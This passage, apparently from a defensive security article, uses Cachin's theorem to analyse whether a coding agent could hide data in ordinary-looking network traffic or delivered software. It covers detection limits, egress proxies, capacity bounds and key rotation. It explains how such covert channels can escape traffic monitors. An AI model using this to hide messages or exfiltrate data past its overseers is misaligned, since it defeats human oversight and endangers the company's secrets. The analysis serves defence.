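For each possible observation *x*, the formula divides the probability of *x* without a message by its probability with one, then averages the logarithm of this ratio over ordinary traffic. The result measures how much evidence ordinary traffic gives, on average, that no message is present. It is zero only if the distributions with and without a message are identical.

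If *D* is zero, no detector can do better than guessing. A detector's decision depends only on what it observes, and each observation is equally likely with or without a message. It therefore raises alarms equally often in both cases, so its recall equals its false positive rate. A detector that catches 90% of messages would also flag 90% of harmless traffic. Its precision would equal the share of all traffic that contains messages, so flagged traffic would be no more likely to contain a message than any other traffic.

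If *D* is small but not zero, a detector can do slightly better. Suppose half of all ordinary messages are long, compared with 60% of those that carry hidden data. For one message, *D* is

0.5 log₂(0.5/0.6) + 0.5 log₂(0.5/0.4),

or about 0.03 bits. Cachin's theorem implies that a detector with no false alarms must miss at least 2⁻ᴰ of the hidden messages, which is about 98%. The evidence adds up if the observer sees many independent messages. After 100 of them, *D* is about 2.9 bits and the lower limit on misses falls to about 13%. A channel that is almost perfectly disguised can therefore become detectable if someone uses it often enough.

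The theorem makes several assumptions that may not hold for a coding agent's work. It assumes that the observer can only watch the traffic, while an egress proxy can block a request or force it into a standard format. It also assumes that the sender and receiver share a secret the observer doesn't know. Finally, it assumes that the observer has no other evidence, but a company may have source code, process records and the agent's transcripts. For example, two programs could produce identical traffic even though only one contains code that reads a password.

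Matching ordinary traffic exactly is also difficult. Cachin describes a method that works without knowing the distribution in advance, but it assumes that the traffic is a series of independent events, and in real network traffic one request often leads to another. The theorem also applies only to callbacks that meet its conditions, and one that contacts a new domain every five seconds plainly doesn't.

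### What a company can establish

The theorem means that clean traffic can't prove a hidden channel is absent. Rice's theorem means that no general method can prove it from source code either. A company could come close to a proof for a small program on a machine with no connections, but few businesses could use such a machine to serve customers.

Putting an upper limit on how much data a hidden channel could carry is more realistic than ruling one out. Suppose a server's only way out is a proxy that sends one partner 50 reports a day at fixed times, and the proxy fixes everything in each report except one eight-byte field. The server can then send at most 400 bytes a day through that field. If the server could also choose when to send the reports, the company would have to add whatever the timing could carry. The limit holds only for channels that someone has thought of, and only while the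 proxy works as intended.

A sandbox doesn't restrict the software an agent hands back. *Tracekit Box* treats that software as a way out of the sandbox, along with the network and credentials. The production server therefore needs its own list of approved destinations. That list should be easier to keep short than the sandbox's, because a payment service needs the same few connections every day, while a coding agent's needs change with each task.

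Frequent key replacement helps protect small secrets. If a 256-bit key expires after 30 minutes, a channel limited to 0.1 bits per second can't finish sending it in time.
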